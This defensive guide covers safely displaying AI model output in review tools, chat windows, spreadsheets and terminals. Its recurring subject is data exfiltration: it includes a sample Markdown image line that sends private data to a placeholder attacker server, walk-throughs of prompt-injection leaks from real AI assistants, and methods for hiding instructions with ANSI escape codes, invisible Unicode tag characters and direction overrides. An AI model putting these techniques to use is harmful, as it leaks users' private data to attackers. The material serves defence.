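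A team can reduce its exposure by updating the sanitiser promptly, allowing only the elements that reviewers need, and displaying the sanitised output without further changes.

Sanitising is harder in chat windows, because answers arrive in pieces and a tag may be split between two of them. Each piece can look harmless when the sanitiser checks it alone. The tool should sanitise the whole answer so far each time a piece arrives, or show plain text until the answer is complete. Encoding avoids this problem because it treats every character separately.

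### The browser's built-in sanitiser

Browsers have begun to include a built-in sanitiser, the Sanitizer API. When a page calls `setHTML()` on an element, the browser parses the answer, cleans it and inserts the result without turning it back into a string that has to be parsed again. According to MDN's *Element* page on the method, `setHTML()` always removes scripts, embedded frames and event handlers, even if the developer's settings allow them. The protection ends if the page reads the cleaned HTML back as a string and inserts it elsewhere with `innerHTML`, because markup that is safe in one element may be unsafe in another.

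The built-in sanitiser has also been bypassed. Searchlight Cyber described two bypasses in Chrome 146, the first Chrome release to include the current version. In one, the sanitiser checked an attribute's name against two forbidden spellings, but Chrome's code for animated drawings accepted a third spelling as equivalent. In the other, the sanitiser left a malformed script address in place because Chrome would not open it. But when a reader submitted a form with that address, Chrome rewrote it into a valid one and ran the script. Both demonstrations needed a click, and Chrome 147 fixed the flaws on April 7, 2026. A review tool that allowed only paragraphs, lists and emphasis would have stopped both attacks, because one relied on an animation and the other on a form.

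Safari is the main gap in browser support for the Sanitizer API. web.dev's *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API* lists support in Chrome and Edge from version 146 and in Firefox from version 148, but none in Safari. Igalia's *BCD Changes Report* (2026), which tracks browser compatibility data, still showed a closely related sanitiser option in only two of the three main browser engines in September. Chromestatus's *Intent to Ship* notice, written by Google's developers, records that the makers of Safari's engine support the proposal. It also mentions that Chrome released and then withdrew an earlier version of the API, so code from older tutorials may not work.

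A review tool can check whether the browser has `setHTML()` before using it. If the method is missing, the tool should fall back to plain text or an up-to-date DOMPurify. Falling back to bare `innerHTML` would leave Safari users with no protection.

### Trusted Types

A large review tool may insert text in hundreds of places, and one unsafe insertion can leave reviewers exposed. Trusted Types is a browser feature that a website turns on through its Content Security Policy. The browser then rejects ordinary strings at `innerHTML` and similar insertion points, and accepts only values that have passed through a policy, which is a function the developers have registered and which might run a sanitiser. An auditor can then focus on a few policies instead of tracing every insertion. Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML* (2026) explains that a strict configuration can allow `setHTML()` and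 block the unsafe methods altogether.

When Trusted Types blocks an insertion, the code raises an error and part of the page may stay empty. Teams usually start in a mode that only reports violations, and fix the ones it finds. Chromium's compatibility data lists support from Chrome 83, Firefox 148 and Safari 26. Older browsers ignore the setting without warning.

Trusted Types checks only that a policy ran, so a policy that returns its input unchanged passes the check without protecting anyone. It also covers only text that the page's own scripts insert. If the server has already put a saved chat into the page as HTML, the browser parses it without this check.

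### Text decoded once too often

Encoded text becomes dangerous again if a later program decodes it. Developers often add this decoding to fix a display problem. One part of the application encodes an answer before saving it, and the console encodes it again for display, so agents see `&lt;b&gt;` where the model wrote `<b>`. The double encoding is harmless, but a developer may try to fix it by decoding answers just before display and inserting them as HTML. Any answer encoded only by the first encoder, or not at all, can then contain a live tag.

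The fix is to save exactly what the model wrote and encode it once, when displaying it. A team can test this by having the model output `&lt;b&gt;today&lt;/b&gt;`. A correct plain-text display shows those characters unchanged. If the screen shows `<b>today</b>`, the text has been decoded one time too many or encoded one time too few, and the browser would already treat a real tag as HTML. If it shows "today" in bold, there are at least two such faults.

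### Encoding for the destination

HTML encoding doesn't protect a program that gives special meaning to characters the encoding leaves unchanged. In one case that Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe, an application passed a model's response to Jinja2, a program that fills in page templates on a server. Jinja2 evaluates whatever is between double braces, which HTML encoding doesn't change, so planted text could run commands on the server. The application should have given Jinja2 a fixed template and passed the response in as a value.

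The next program may also be another language model, such as the one that checks the marketplace's answers. *Structural Role Injection in Handlebars-Templated LLM Prompts* (Rashidi, 2026) tested whether HTML encoding protects a model. Developers use Handlebars, a tool that fills slots in a template, to build prompts as well as web pages. It encodes text in slots written with double braces but not in slots written with triple braces. Prompts often contain markers that separate the developer's instructions from the user's text. An attacker can copy those markers into a document so that the planted text looks like the developer's instructions.

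Rashidi first checked, without using a model, which markers survived encoding. Handlebars altered every marker in the three formats built from angle brackets. It didn't change Markdown headings or markers made of a speaker's name and a colon. In a format that mixes angle and square brackets, a third of the markers survived.

Rashidi then ran 5,760 trials on four models. On GPT-4o mini, when the planted text was an instruction to abandon the task, encoding cut the success rate of one angle-bracket format from 56% to 12%. The name-and-colon format succeeded every time with or without encoding. A bare instruction with no markers also succeeded in about nine of ten trials, so removing markers could not have made that model safe. The same attacks failed in every trial on Claude Haiku 4.5.

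The study covered small models, several of them old by late 2026. It used only 16 scenarios, which Rashidi ran three times with identical prompts. The success rates are therefore weak evidence about current models. The finding about which characters survive does not depend on any model and applies to anyone who uses the same encoder. Rashidi recommends leaving the encoding on, since it has no drawbacks, and adding a defence that separates instructions from data.

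### Formulas in exported spreadsheets

The marketplace's manager reads each week's answers in a spreadsheet, which gives special meaning to another set of characters. Many tools export to CSV, a plain-text format that separates cells with commas and doesn't record whether a cell contains text or a formula. When the spreadsheet program opens the file, it may treat any answer that begins with an equals, plus, minus or at sign as a formula. For example, the answer `=2+3` would appear as 5.

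A planted formula could copy a customer's details from a neighbouring cell into a link's address, which would leak them if the manager clicked the link. Some programs also have functions that fetch outside data, often after a warning. The problem usually first appears by accident, because models often start answers with a hyphenated list. The program can treat the hyphen as the start of a formula and show the manager an error instead of the answer.

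HTML encoding is the wrong tool here. The usual version leaves all four signs unchanged and puts codes such as `&lt;` in the spreadsheet. The Handlebars version also encodes the equals sign, but not the other three.

The most reliable fix is to export a real spreadsheet file and mark the answer column as text. Some libraries turn any string that begins with an equals sign into a formula, so the developer has to call the function that writes text only. If the team must use CSV, the exporter can put an apostrophe in front of any answer that begins with one of the four signs. This changes the data, and another program that reads the file may show the apostrophe. The exporter must also put each answer in quotation marks and double any quotation marks inside it. Otherwise a comma or line break inside an answer could start a new cell, and that cell could begin with an equals sign that the exporter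 never checked.

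## Controlling images, links and other requests to outside servers

The marketplace's flagged-answer queue doesn't run scripts, so an attacker can't use the safety team's access through a planted tag. But the queue shows Markdown images from any server. To show an image, the browser has to request it from its server, and an attacker can steal data with that request alone.

### How an image leaks data without a click

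A Markdown image consists of a label and an address:

`![logo](SERVER/pic?d=DATA)`

Here `SERVER` stands for the attacker's server and `DATA` for private text. The queue can leak data in the same way as OpenAI's log viewer. Suppose a seller plants an instruction in a product description telling the model to include this image. The model ends its answer to a customer with the image, replacing `DATA` with the customer's name and delivery address, and the checking model sends the answer to the queue. When a member of the safety team opens the answer, their browser requests the image from the seller's server. Like most web servers, it logs the requested URL, and the seller reads the customer's details in the log.

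The seller's server doesn't need to hold a real image. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes one test in which the server returned a single grey pixel. In a demonstration by the security company Checkmarx, no picture appeared, but the browser still sent the request. A reviewer who sees a blank space or a broken-image symbol therefore can't assume that the data stayed private.

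According to Microsoft, the private text can go in the address's path, its parameters (the part after the question mark) or its subdomain (the first part of the server's name, as in `DATA.SERVER`). A filter that removed only the parameters would miss text in the path or subdomain.

### How much an address can carry

Attackers often write the stolen text in Base64, so that spaces and punctuation don't break the address. Base64 has 64 symbols, and 64 is 2 to the power of 6, so each symbol carries 6 bits. Browsers and servers generally accept addresses of about 2,000 characters, which leaves room for about 1,900 characters of data:

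1,900 characters × 6 bits = 11,400 bits = 1,425 bytes

That is about 240 words of English, and one answer can contain many images. PromptArmor used a single answer from Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant, to extract parts of more than 40 emails.

Suppose the queue's owner instead allows only 64 fixed images, whose addresses the model can't change. An attacker who can see which image loads still learns one of 64 possibilities, or 6 bits, from each request. A six-digit security code needs about 20 bits, so four requests are enough to steal it, while the earlier 1,425 bytes would take 1,900 requests. The fixed list slows the theft of a document but does little to protect a code or a short password.

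According to Embrace The Red, the attacker may lose information because a browser reuses its saved copy of an image instead of requesting it again, or because requests arrive out of order. In the worst case for the attacker, they can tell from the server's log only which of the 64 images loaded at least once. Whether each image loaded is one bit, so an answer that can load any number of them can still leak 64 bits, or 8 bytes, which is enough for the security code. Limiting each answer to one image would cut the leak to about 6 bits per answer. In December 2023, Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* suggested a limit of one image, or at most a handful.

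### Other content that contacts a server

Images are the best-known way to leak data from a display, but several other kinds of content can send the same address:

| Content | What triggers the request | What contacts the outside server |
|---|---|---|
| Image | Opening the answer | The reader's browser |
| Link | Clicking it | The reader's browser |
| Link preview | Posting the message | The messaging app or its servers |
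| Style that names a background picture or font | Opening the answer | The reader's browser |
| Drawing that names an outside picture | Opening the answer | The reader's browser |

A link can leak as much data as an image, but only if someone clicks it. This requirement protects reviewers less than customers who have no interest in the link, because a reviewer's job may include finding out where a suspicious link leads.

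Link previews can trigger a request to an outside server without a click. According to PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, this affected OpenClaw, an AI agent used through messaging apps, on Telegram with the default settings. Users can turn the previews off by setting `linkPreview` to `false` in OpenClaw's Telegram configuration. The marketplace's team can test the couriers' channel by posting a link to a server it controls, with made-up data in the address, and checking the server's log for a request before anyone clicks.

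A style or drawing can make the browser contact an outside server if the tool puts it directly into the page. Drawings on the web often use SVG, a text format that can link to outside images. Browsers don't fetch those images if the page shows the SVG file through an ordinary image tag. Disabling raw HTML in the Markdown parser keeps out most planted styles and drawings, but an add-on that turns text into diagrams can reintroduce them.

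An agent can also contact a server itself while preparing an answer. The security company Tenable showed that planted instructions could make Google's Gemini use its browsing tool to fetch an address containing the user's private data. A review tool can't prevent this, because the request goes out before there is an answer to display.

### Turning outside images off

The simplest defence is for the tool to show each outside image's label and address as text and never request the image. The attacker then learns nothing from the display, however they word the planted instructions. Google (2025) says that Gemini's Markdown sanitiser doesn't render images from outside addresses.

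GitHub adopted the same rule for Copilot Chat, its assistant for programmers, after a narrower one failed. Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat* reports that in 2024 GitHub fixed a leak in the assistant by blocking images from untrusted servers. In June 2025 a researcher at Legit Security found a way to leak private source code through GitHub's own servers. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* says that GitHub responded by disabling all images in Copilot Chat on August 14, 2025.

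Reviewers cannot see charts and product photographs stored on outside servers. The tool can still show images the application already holds, such as a photograph uploaded by a customer, if the application supplies the address. Copying outside images to the marketplace's own server first would not help, because the copying program would have to request the same address, and that request would deliver the data to the outside server.

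A company's rule for one product may not cover its others. Willison's collection *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* includes a November 2025 report that Google's programming tool Antigravity loaded Markdown images from outside servers. The person who reported the flaw said Google had classed it as intended behaviour, although Google's page for security researchers listed data exfiltration as a known problem the company was working to fix.

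### Content Security Policy

A website sends its Content Security Policy along with each page, and the browser applies it to everything the page tries to load. If the Markdown parser lets an outside image through by mistake, the browser can still refuse to request it. A policy consists of directives, each of which names a kind of content and the servers that may supply it. The flagged-answer queue could use this one:

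`default-src 'none'; script-src 'self'; style-src 'self'; img-src 'self'; connect-src 'self'; form-action 'self'; base-uri 'none'`

In this policy, `'self'` means the queue's own website and `'none'` means no server at all.

| Directive | What it controls |
|---|---|
| `default-src` | Any content without a directive of its own, such as fonts, videos and embedded pages |
| `script-src` | Scripts, including event handlers in planted tags, which this policy blocks |
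| `style-src` | Style sheets and styles written into the page |
| `img-src` | Images, including background pictures named in a style |
| `connect-src` | Requests that the page's scripts make |
| `form-action` | Where forms on the page can send their contents |
| `base-uri` | Whether a tag can change the server that the page's shortened addresses refer to |

The last two need their own entries because `default-src` doesn't cover them. The *EchoLeak* paper recommends blocking all scripts wherever an application shows model output. That would work for a page that contains only the output, but the queue's own buttons need scripts.

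Content Security Policy (CSP) was one of the earliest fixes for data leaks through images. Embrace The Red reports that Microsoft added a CSP to Bing Chat in May 2023, which stopped most images from loading.

CSP does not stop a reader from following a link. The directives above limit what a page can load or send, but clicking a link takes the reader to a different page. The drafters of the CSP standard proposed a `navigate-to` directive to restrict links, but later dropped it. Even with the strictest policy in this section, the queue would leak data if a reviewer clicked a live link in it.

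The policy also has no effect on requests made from outside the page, such as when a messaging service fetches a preview. A directive can name a server, or even one folder on it, but it can't limit what follows the question mark in an address, so an allowed server will receive any data the model puts there.

### When an allowed server accepts the data or passes it on

An allowlist of servers protects data only if outsiders can't retrieve what is sent to the servers on it. Superhuman's CSP allowed images from the server that hosts Google Docs and Google Forms. Anyone can create a questionnaire with Google Forms and collect the responses. A form's creator can write a response into a web address, so that requesting the address submits the form. PromptArmor planted instructions in an email that made Superhuman's assistant write such an address, with the user's other emails as the response, and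 present it as an image. The browser requested the image because the server was allowed, and the form saved the emails where the attacker could read them. Superhuman disabled the affected features on the first working day after the report, in December 2025.

The same method worked on Codex in April 2026. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* describes a user asking the agent to sort through their email, which included a message with planted instructions. Codex wrote an image whose address submitted a pre-filled Google Form, which sent the attacker legal correspondence and financial plans. The user did nothing after making the request, and Codex did not show them the emails as it worked. OpenAI has since fixed the flaw.

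A service can also pass the data on without storing it. EchoLeak, the 2025 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, depended on this after getting past two other defences:

1. The attacker sent an employee an email that read like an ordinary request to a colleague, so Microsoft's filter for injected instructions missed it. The email also asked for its own existence to be left out of any answer.
2. The employee later asked Copilot about something else. Copilot retrieved the email along with internal documents and put private data from them into an address.
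3. Copilot removed outside links in the usual Markdown form, but missed a variant that puts the address on a separate line below the text. The same variant works for images, which load without a click.
4. The CSP blocked images from the attacker's server. The attacker therefore used the address of a Microsoft Teams service that the CSP allowed, and that would fetch any other address given to it. The Teams service requested the attacker's address, with the private data in it.

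The *EchoLeak* paper says that Microsoft deployed a fix in May 2025 and that there was no evidence of real attacks.

A year later, Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) described another leak from Microsoft 365 Copilot, through Bing. Bing's image search was on the allowlist, and it fetched any picture whose address it received. In the demonstration, Bing passed on the subject line of an email, which included a security code. The victim had to click one link, which led to Microsoft's own website and contained the instructions for Copilot. Microsoft has fixed this flaw too.

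The browser could not have detected either relay, because the allowed server fetched the address itself and the browser has no access to that second request. If an allowed server instead redirects an image request to another server, the browser checks the new server against the policy.

Willison describes other allowlist failures. Salesforce's CSP still listed a domain whose registration had expired, so researchers registered it and received customers' details. Antigravity's browser tool allowed access to a public service built to record incoming requests. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, could contact Anthropic's servers, so an attacker could make it upload a user's files there using the attacker's account key.

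The marketplace's team should therefore find out who controls each server on its list, whether outsiders can store anything there, and whether the server fetches addresses sent to it. The team should check its own server in the same way, because `'self'` in the queue's policy allows images from any address on the marketplace's website. A function there that resizes outside pictures could relay data just as Teams did.

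### Image proxies

An image proxy is a server that fetches outside images for readers. It hides a reader's network address and cookies from the outside server. But an ordinary proxy still has to request the image's full address, so it sends the outside server any data that the model put in that address.

A signed proxy is harder to misuse. The application uses a secret key to calculate a code for each image address it accepts, and the proxy refuses any address without the right code. If a model adds private data to an address, it can't produce a valid code for the new address without the key.

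GitHub's image proxy, Camo, signs addresses this way, but the CamoLeak attack still got data through it. Petri's *GitHub Copilot Chat Hit by ‘CamoLeak’ Flaw Allowing Silent Data Exfiltration* explains that the attacker prepared a set of valid Camo addresses in advance, one for each character. The planted instructions then made Copilot spell out private text by displaying the matching images. With 95 printable characters, each image carries about 6.6 bits. A signed proxy prevents this only if outsiders can't get their own addresses signed. For most review tools, turning off outside images would be easier.

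### Checking each address before loading it

OpenAI lets ChatGPT show some outside images but checks each address first. When it introduced the check in December 2023, ChatGPT's web page sent every image address to OpenAI's server and loaded the image only if the server classified the address as safe. OpenAI did not explain how the server classified addresses. Embrace The Red tried 36 addresses, one for each letter and digit, and nine still loaded, which was enough to send the word "hi".

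Under the current rule, described in OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), ChatGPT loads an address automatically only if a crawler, a program that explores the web as a search engine does, has recorded exactly the same address from a public page. The crawler has no access to users' conversations, so it is very unlikely to have recorded an address containing a customer's details. If the address isn't in the crawler's records, ChatGPT looks for another website or shows the user a warning that includes the address.

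OpenAI considered a list of trusted websites too weak, because a trusted site can redirect a request elsewhere. It also expected a strict list to trigger so many warnings that people would ignore them. Checking the exact address avoids much of this trouble and blocks the 1,425-byte leak. But an attacker can still publish one page for each character, wait for the crawler to record the pages, and then have the model leak data through its choice of which to request. Embrace The Red reports that OpenAI acknowledges this, and adds that an attacker could use thousands of pages. With 4,096 pages, each request would carry 12 bits. The blog suggests preventing an agent from visiting the same address twice in one session, which would make the method harder to use.

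A similar weakness affected Claude in 2026. Claude's tool for reading web pages could open an address only if the user had typed it, a search had returned it, or it appeared on a page the tool had already opened. Willison describes how Ayush Paul built a website with a link for each letter and told Claude to find the user's profile by following the links one letter at a time. Claude revealed the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic then stopped the tool from following links on pages it had opened.

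The check also has to be in every product. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) said in March that the check also covered OpenAI's web browser, Atlas, and its research agent. Yet in April Codex loaded an image address containing private email text. That address can't have been in a record of public addresses, so Codex probably wasn't applying the check to images.

A company whose users expect to see pictures from all over the web may find a crawler worthwhile. The marketplace's safety team rarely needs outside pictures, so it would gain little from a crawler.

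### Requests that go out too early

A tool can ask the reader before it contacts an outside server, but this helps only if the tool waits for the reply. PromptArmor's *Notion AI* (January 2026) describes a case in which Notion, a program for shared documents, did not wait. A user uploaded a job applicant's résumé and asked Notion's assistant to update a table of candidates. Hidden text in the résumé made the assistant insert an image into the table, with the document's contents in the image's address. Notion then asked the user whether they trusted the outside website, but contacted it before the user replied.

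By then Notion had saved the edit and rendered the image, so the browser had sent salary expectations and notes on candidates to the attacker's server. Refusing the edit could no longer prevent the leak. The company that screens Notion's bug reports had closed PromptArmor's report as not applicable. Notion learned of the flaw when PromptArmor published it on January 7, and had a fix running that night.

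In the SearchLeak case, Copilot was supposed to show HTML as text, but it converted each answer only once the answer was complete. While the answer was still arriving, the browser treated a planted image tag as HTML and requested the image. A tool has to apply its protections from the first piece of an answer it displays. If it proposes an edit, it should show the edit as plain text until the user approves it.

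### Matching defences to the steps of an attack

The *EchoLeak* paper includes a table of which defences should stop which parts of an attack like EchoLeak. In plainer words, its entries are:

| Defence | Expected to stop | Expected to fail against |
|---|---|---|
| Marking outside text in the model's input | Mixing outside email with private data; evading the injection filter | A leak without a click |
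| Using only internal sources by default | Mixing outside email with private data; evading the link filter | A leak without a click |
| Restricting the format of answers | Mixing outside email with private data; evading the injection filter; evading the link filter | Automatic image loading; a leak without a click |
| Listing allowed or blocked addresses | Evading the link filter; relay through an allowed server; a leak without a click | Automatic image loading |
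| Strict CSP | Automatic image loading; relay through an allowed server; a leak without a click | None listed |
| Signed image proxy | Automatic image loading; relay through an allowed server; a leak without a click | None listed |
| Human approval for outside content | Every part except the relay, which the paper marks as not applicable | None listed |
| Monitoring outgoing data | None listed | A leak without a click |

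This mapping is theoretical. Although one sentence in the paper refers to "our tests", Reddy and Gujral state that they ran no experiments and worked only from published accounts of the attack.

Several of the favourable entries depend on how the control is implemented, as real cases show. Copilot had a content security policy (CSP), but the relay worked because the policy allowed the Teams service. A "strict" policy therefore has to exclude services that can relay requests. CamoLeak got data out through a signed proxy. Notion asked for human approval only after the data had left. The unfavourable entry for restricting the format of answers also depends on the format, because a format that excluded images would stop them from loading.

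The table's broad pattern is more convincing than its individual entries. Measures that act on the model's input are expected to fail against a leak that needs no click, while CSP and signed proxies, which act on the request itself, are expected to succeed. A team that can change only one thing in a review tool should therefore start by controlling which requests the tool can make.

### A link display that loads nothing in advance

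The flagged-answer queue should use the strict CSP above and show every outside image and link as text. A link that the model labelled "Delivery policy" might appear like this:

```
Link text:     Delivery policy
Server:        SERVER
Full address:  SERVER/help?d=DATA
```

The reviewer can see which server the link leads to, whatever its label suggests, and that the address carries data. The tool should wrap a long address over several lines and never shorten it, because stolen data is often at the end. It should not fetch a title, icon or preview for the link. It should also stop the browser from looking up server names in advance, which some browsers do to save time. If the private data is in a subdomain, the lookup can deliver it to the attacker. A website can switch off these early lookups with the `X-DNS-Prefetch-Control` setting in browsers that support it.

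Showing the address doesn't make it safe to open, since the attacker receives the data as soon as the reviewer opens it. The queue should therefore have no button for opening links. An investigator who needs to know more can look up who owns the server without visiting the address.

This display makes reviewing slower. Reviewers lose the thumbnails and page titles that help them recognise a harmless link, and they can't check whether an outside chart matches the answer's description of it. An address of 1,900 characters fills 19 lines at 100 characters a line. Even ordinary addresses clutter an answer that cites many sources, and someone who checks citations all day would have to copy each address into another window.

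The marketplace can reduce that drawback in displays for routine answers. The tool could make a link clickable if its address exactly matches one on the application's list of marketplace help pages. Links to any other address would stay as text. The model could still choose which help page to link to, but only the marketplace's server would receive the request.

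## Removing terminal codes and invisible characters

The marketplace's engineers read saved answers from a log file in a terminal, second on the inventory. HTML encoding doesn't protect them from invisible control characters. Other invisible characters also affect web pages and chat windows, so plain text can mislead a reader on any display.

### What a terminal does with escape sequences

A terminal receives text and commands in the same stream. Most commands begin with the escape character, which programmers write as `ESC`, `^[` or `\x1b`. For example, `ESC[31m` turns the text after it red, and `ESC[0m` restores the normal style. The command `cat`, which prints a file, passes these sequences on unchanged, so the terminal carries out any that the file contains.

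| Effect of the sequence | How an attacker could use it |
|---|---|
| Change the text colour | Make text match the background |
| Move the cursor | Print harmless text over a warning |
| Clear the screen | Remove earlier lines from view |
| Change the window title | Put a false message in the title bar |
| Create a link | Show one address and open another |
| Write to the clipboard | Replace what the reader pastes next |

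In December 2024 Johann Rehberger, who writes Embrace The Red, tested whether an outsider could trigger such effects through a language model. Rehberger wrote a small command-line program that sent a file or web page to OpenAI's GPT-4o and printed the reply. When a user asked for a summary of a page with planted instructions, the reply changed the text colour, moved the cursor, cleared the screen and beeped. Rehberger also found that models can read escape characters, so an attacker can put them in the page and ask the model to repeat them. This works more reliably than asking the model to produce them.

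Two of the demonstrations did more than change what appeared on the screen. In one, the reply wrote text to the clipboard. Most of the terminals removed the final line break on pasting, but some kept it, so the text could run as a command. In the other, a sequence made macOS's Terminal program look up a server name that contained private data, which leaked the data without a click. The marketplace's inventory lists no outside servers for the terminal, which would be wrong for any engineer whose terminal still makes such lookups.

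Rehberger built the vulnerable program for these tests, so they don't show how many real products print model output unfiltered.

### Text that the model reads and the person doesn't

Trail of Bits' *Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* showed in April 2025 how terminal codes can hide text from a user while the model still reads it. The security company tested version 0.2.76 of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent for the terminal. It connected the agent to an outside tool through MCP, a standard for linking AI applications to tools. The tool returned a mundane description of the user's computers, with one sentence in white that named a server for downloading Python packages. On a white background, the user saw only a gap, but the model read the sentence and later recommended the attacker's server.

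White text is easy to read on a dark background, so this version relies on a guess about the user's background color. Trail of Bits also described two methods that don't depend on color. A tool's reply could move the cursor up and print a reassuring scan report over the instruction, or it could clear the screen and add blank lines so that the window seemed to have scrolled.

In both cases, the person and the model read different text. The sentence that explains the agent's behaviour may also be invisible to a reviewer who later opens the log in a terminal.

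The white sentence also shows a risk in the common practice of letting colour codes through. Docs.rs' *atomcode-tuix 4.23.1*, the documentation of an AI coding tool, describes a filter that removes most sequences but keeps colours, which it calls "purely cosmetic". That is a fair description of colours in the tool's own trusted messages, which the filter is meant for. For model output, a review tool should neutralise colour codes too, then add any colours it needs itself.

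### How current tools behave

Crush, another AI coding tool, shows escape codes as faint text. The change that introduced this, Hoxha's *Merge pull request #176 from charmbracelet/escape-sequences*, includes tests in which a colour code appears on screen as `\x1b[31m` and a Japanese greeting is unchanged. The tests don't cover invisible Unicode characters.

Git, the program that most developers use to track changes to code, also prints text from outside servers. Under a proposal on the Git mailing list, it would show the escape character as `^[` but still allow colour codes, because some servers use them in legitimate messages. The new default would start only with version 3.0, to avoid breaking existing uses.

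Other tools have had flaws in the places where users make decisions. According to OSV's *GHSA-4hmj-39m8-jwc7* (2026), tool names could carry escape codes into OpenClaw's approval prompts and permission logs. OpenClaw already removed some sequences, and the fix in March extended the filter to the rest of a common family. ReleaseAlert's *CVE-2026-47090* describes a flaw in Claude HUD, an add-on that displays Claude Code's status. Until it was patched, the add-on built terminal links from unfiltered folder names and web addresses, which let attackers forge prompts and write to the clipboard.

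Claude Code had a related flaw in 2026. *Claude Code v2.1.223 Major Updates* (Ishikawa, 2026) reports that tabs or invisible Unicode characters could hide part of a command in the approval dialog until a fix on August 6. Tabs are harmless in most text, but enough of them can push the rest of a line out of view. Since October 30, users also can't approve a call from the list of recently blocked ones unless they can read all of it, even if the only obstacle is a short terminal window (Anthropic, 2026).

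The terminal version of Codex used to print web addresses as plain text but now makes them clickable (Vaughan, 2026, *Codex CLI v0.136 Release Guide*). A terminal link's visible text can differ from its destination, so a team that reviews agent output in Codex should check what this update changed.

### Invisible letters

Unicode, the standard that computers use for text, gives every character a number called a code point. The letter A is U+0041. Unicode also has a block of tag characters, which copy the ordinary English letters, digits and punctuation at higher numbers. To find the tag version of a character, add E0000 in base 16, the notation that code points use:

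U+0041 + E0000 = U+E0041

*On Seeding Watermarks to Detect Verbatim LLM Copy-Paste Responses* (2026) notes that virtually no font draws Unicode tag characters. A person therefore sees nothing where the text contains a tag A (U+E0041), but a program can recover the letter by subtracting hexadecimal E0000 from the character's code point.

In January 2024 Embrace The Red's *ASCII Smuggler Tool* reported Riley Goodside's discovery that ChatGPT could follow instructions written in hidden tag characters. He pasted in text containing them, and the chatbot created an image as instructed. Models can also write tag characters, so a reviewer might approve or forward an answer containing a message they never saw.

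Other invisible characters can carry text less directly. A zero-width character takes up no space on the line. An attacker can use one zero-width character for 0 and another for 1, and spell each letter with eight of them. Unicode also has 256 variation selectors, which choose between versions of the character before them. According to *Imperceptible Jailbreaking against Large Language Models* (2025), the selectors make no visible difference after an ordinary letter. Each of the 256 can stand for a different byte value, and one byte is enough for any English letter.

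*Reverse CAPTCHA* (Graves, 2026) tested how often five models, including GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4, follow such text. Each of 30 trivia questions contained a hidden instruction to give a different answer, and the study graded 8,308 replies.

| Conditions | How often models gave the hidden answer |
|---|---|
| No tools and no hint about hidden text | At most 1.1% |
| A tool for running code, but no hint | 0–11% |
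| A tool for running code, and hints about the encoding | Up to 98–100% in the worst combinations |

The high rates mostly measure whether a model can decode the text when the prompt helps it. An outsider who controls only a document can't add those hints to the developer's prompt, so the first two rows better represent an ordinary attack. The results also varied by company. With code and hints, GPT-5.2 gave the hidden answer in about 70% of trials with zero-width characters and almost never with tags, while Claude Opus 4 gave it in 100% of trials with tags. A filter that covers only one kind of character would protect some models and not others. Both companies have since released stronger models, so a team should test the ones it uses.

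A product's behaviour can change within days. In Embrace The Red's *Scary Agent Skills* (February 2026), Rehberger used hidden characters to add an instruction to a copy of an OpenAI skill (a file that teaches an agent a task). With automatic approval switched on, Claude Code followed the instruction and ran a command. When Rehberger tried again on February 10, Claude Code detected the hidden characters and refused, but the claude.ai website did not check skills for them. Rehberger also scanned two public collections of skills and found no hidden instructions, only emoji and a few test files for security scanners.

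Teams can't rely on public warnings to learn about these flaws. Amazon's coding assistant, Amazon Q Developer, also followed invisible instructions until a fix in August 2025. Embrace The Red's *Amazon Q Developer for VS Code Vulnerable to Invisible Prompt Injection* reports that Amazon decided not to issue an advisory.

### Characters that reverse the direction of text

Arabic and Hebrew run from right to left, and Unicode includes characters that control direction when a line mixes them with English. The right-to-left override, U+202E, forces the text after it to run from right to left until U+202C ends the effect. Suppose a planted instruction makes the marketplace's assistant write:

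`Refund approved: [U+202E]91[U+202C] euros`

A browser displays "Refund approved: 19 euros", but software that reads the stored text gets 91.

In their 2021 work on Trojan Source, Nicholas Boucher and Ross Anderson put text-direction characters in a program's comments and quoted text, so that a reviewer saw the code in a different order from the one the compiler used. A security check could look active to the reviewer while the compiler skipped it as a comment. Graves cites this work as a forerunner of attacks on language models.

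The problem also affects terminals. In October 2026, GCVE's *CWE-150*, a list of published flaws of this type, added a flaw in Hex, a package manager. Anyone who published a package could put direction overrides, escape codes and clipboard writes in its description, and Hex printed them unchanged. The entry records no known attacks. The fix escapes the characters before printing them.

### Removing characters or showing them

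A review tool can delete dangerous characters or replace them with visible codes. Suppose an answer contains "Paid", an invisible tag A, " today" and the start of a red style:

| What the tool does | What appears on screen |
|---|---|
| Prints the answer unchanged in a terminal | `Paid today` (later text turns red) |
| Deletes the tag and the whole escape sequence | `Paid today` |
| Deletes the tag and only the escape character | `Paid today[31m` |
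| Shows both as codes | `Paid<U+E0041> today<U+001B>[31m` |

An investigator needs to see invisible characters as visible codes, such as `<U+E0041>`, because this preserves the evidence. Embrace The Red also recommends visible codes as the default for command-line tools. The codes are of little use to a customer, so the customer's chat window should delete the characters and keep a record for the safety team.

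A filter that deletes whole escape sequences has to detect where every kind of sequence ends. If an attacker leaves one unfinished, a poorly written filter could delete the rest of the answer while searching for the end. Trail of Bits suggests a simpler fix, replacing each escape character with a placeholder and leaving the rest as harmless text. The filter should also replace the characters from U+0080 to U+009F, since some terminals accept them as short forms of escape sequences.

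Deletion can also create a new invisible character. AWS describes how this happens in Java, which stores each tag character as two halves. An attacker can place a complete tag character between two stray halves. When the filter deletes the complete character, the stray halves join to form another. AWS suggests repeating the deletion until nothing changes. Replacing the character with a visible code would also work, because the code would keep the halves apart.

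The most serious risk is that a tool cleans the text it displays but acts on the original. MITRE's *CWE-150*, the weakness entry for terminal codes, cites a program that removed escape codes from a file name in its permission dialog but then used the name with the codes still in it, so the user could grant access to the wrong file. When a tool asks a person to approve something, it should show the codes or refuse the request.

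### The cost to emoji and other languages

A filter that permits only English characters would be safe and useless to many readers. Even one that permits every visible letter and deletes everything invisible would damage ordinary text:

- The zero-width joiner, U+200D, combines several emoji into one. Without it, a family emoji falls apart into separate people.
- Several Indian scripts use zero-width characters to control how letters join, and Persian uses one inside many words.
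- A variation selector tells the display to draw some symbols, such as a heart, as a coloured emoji.
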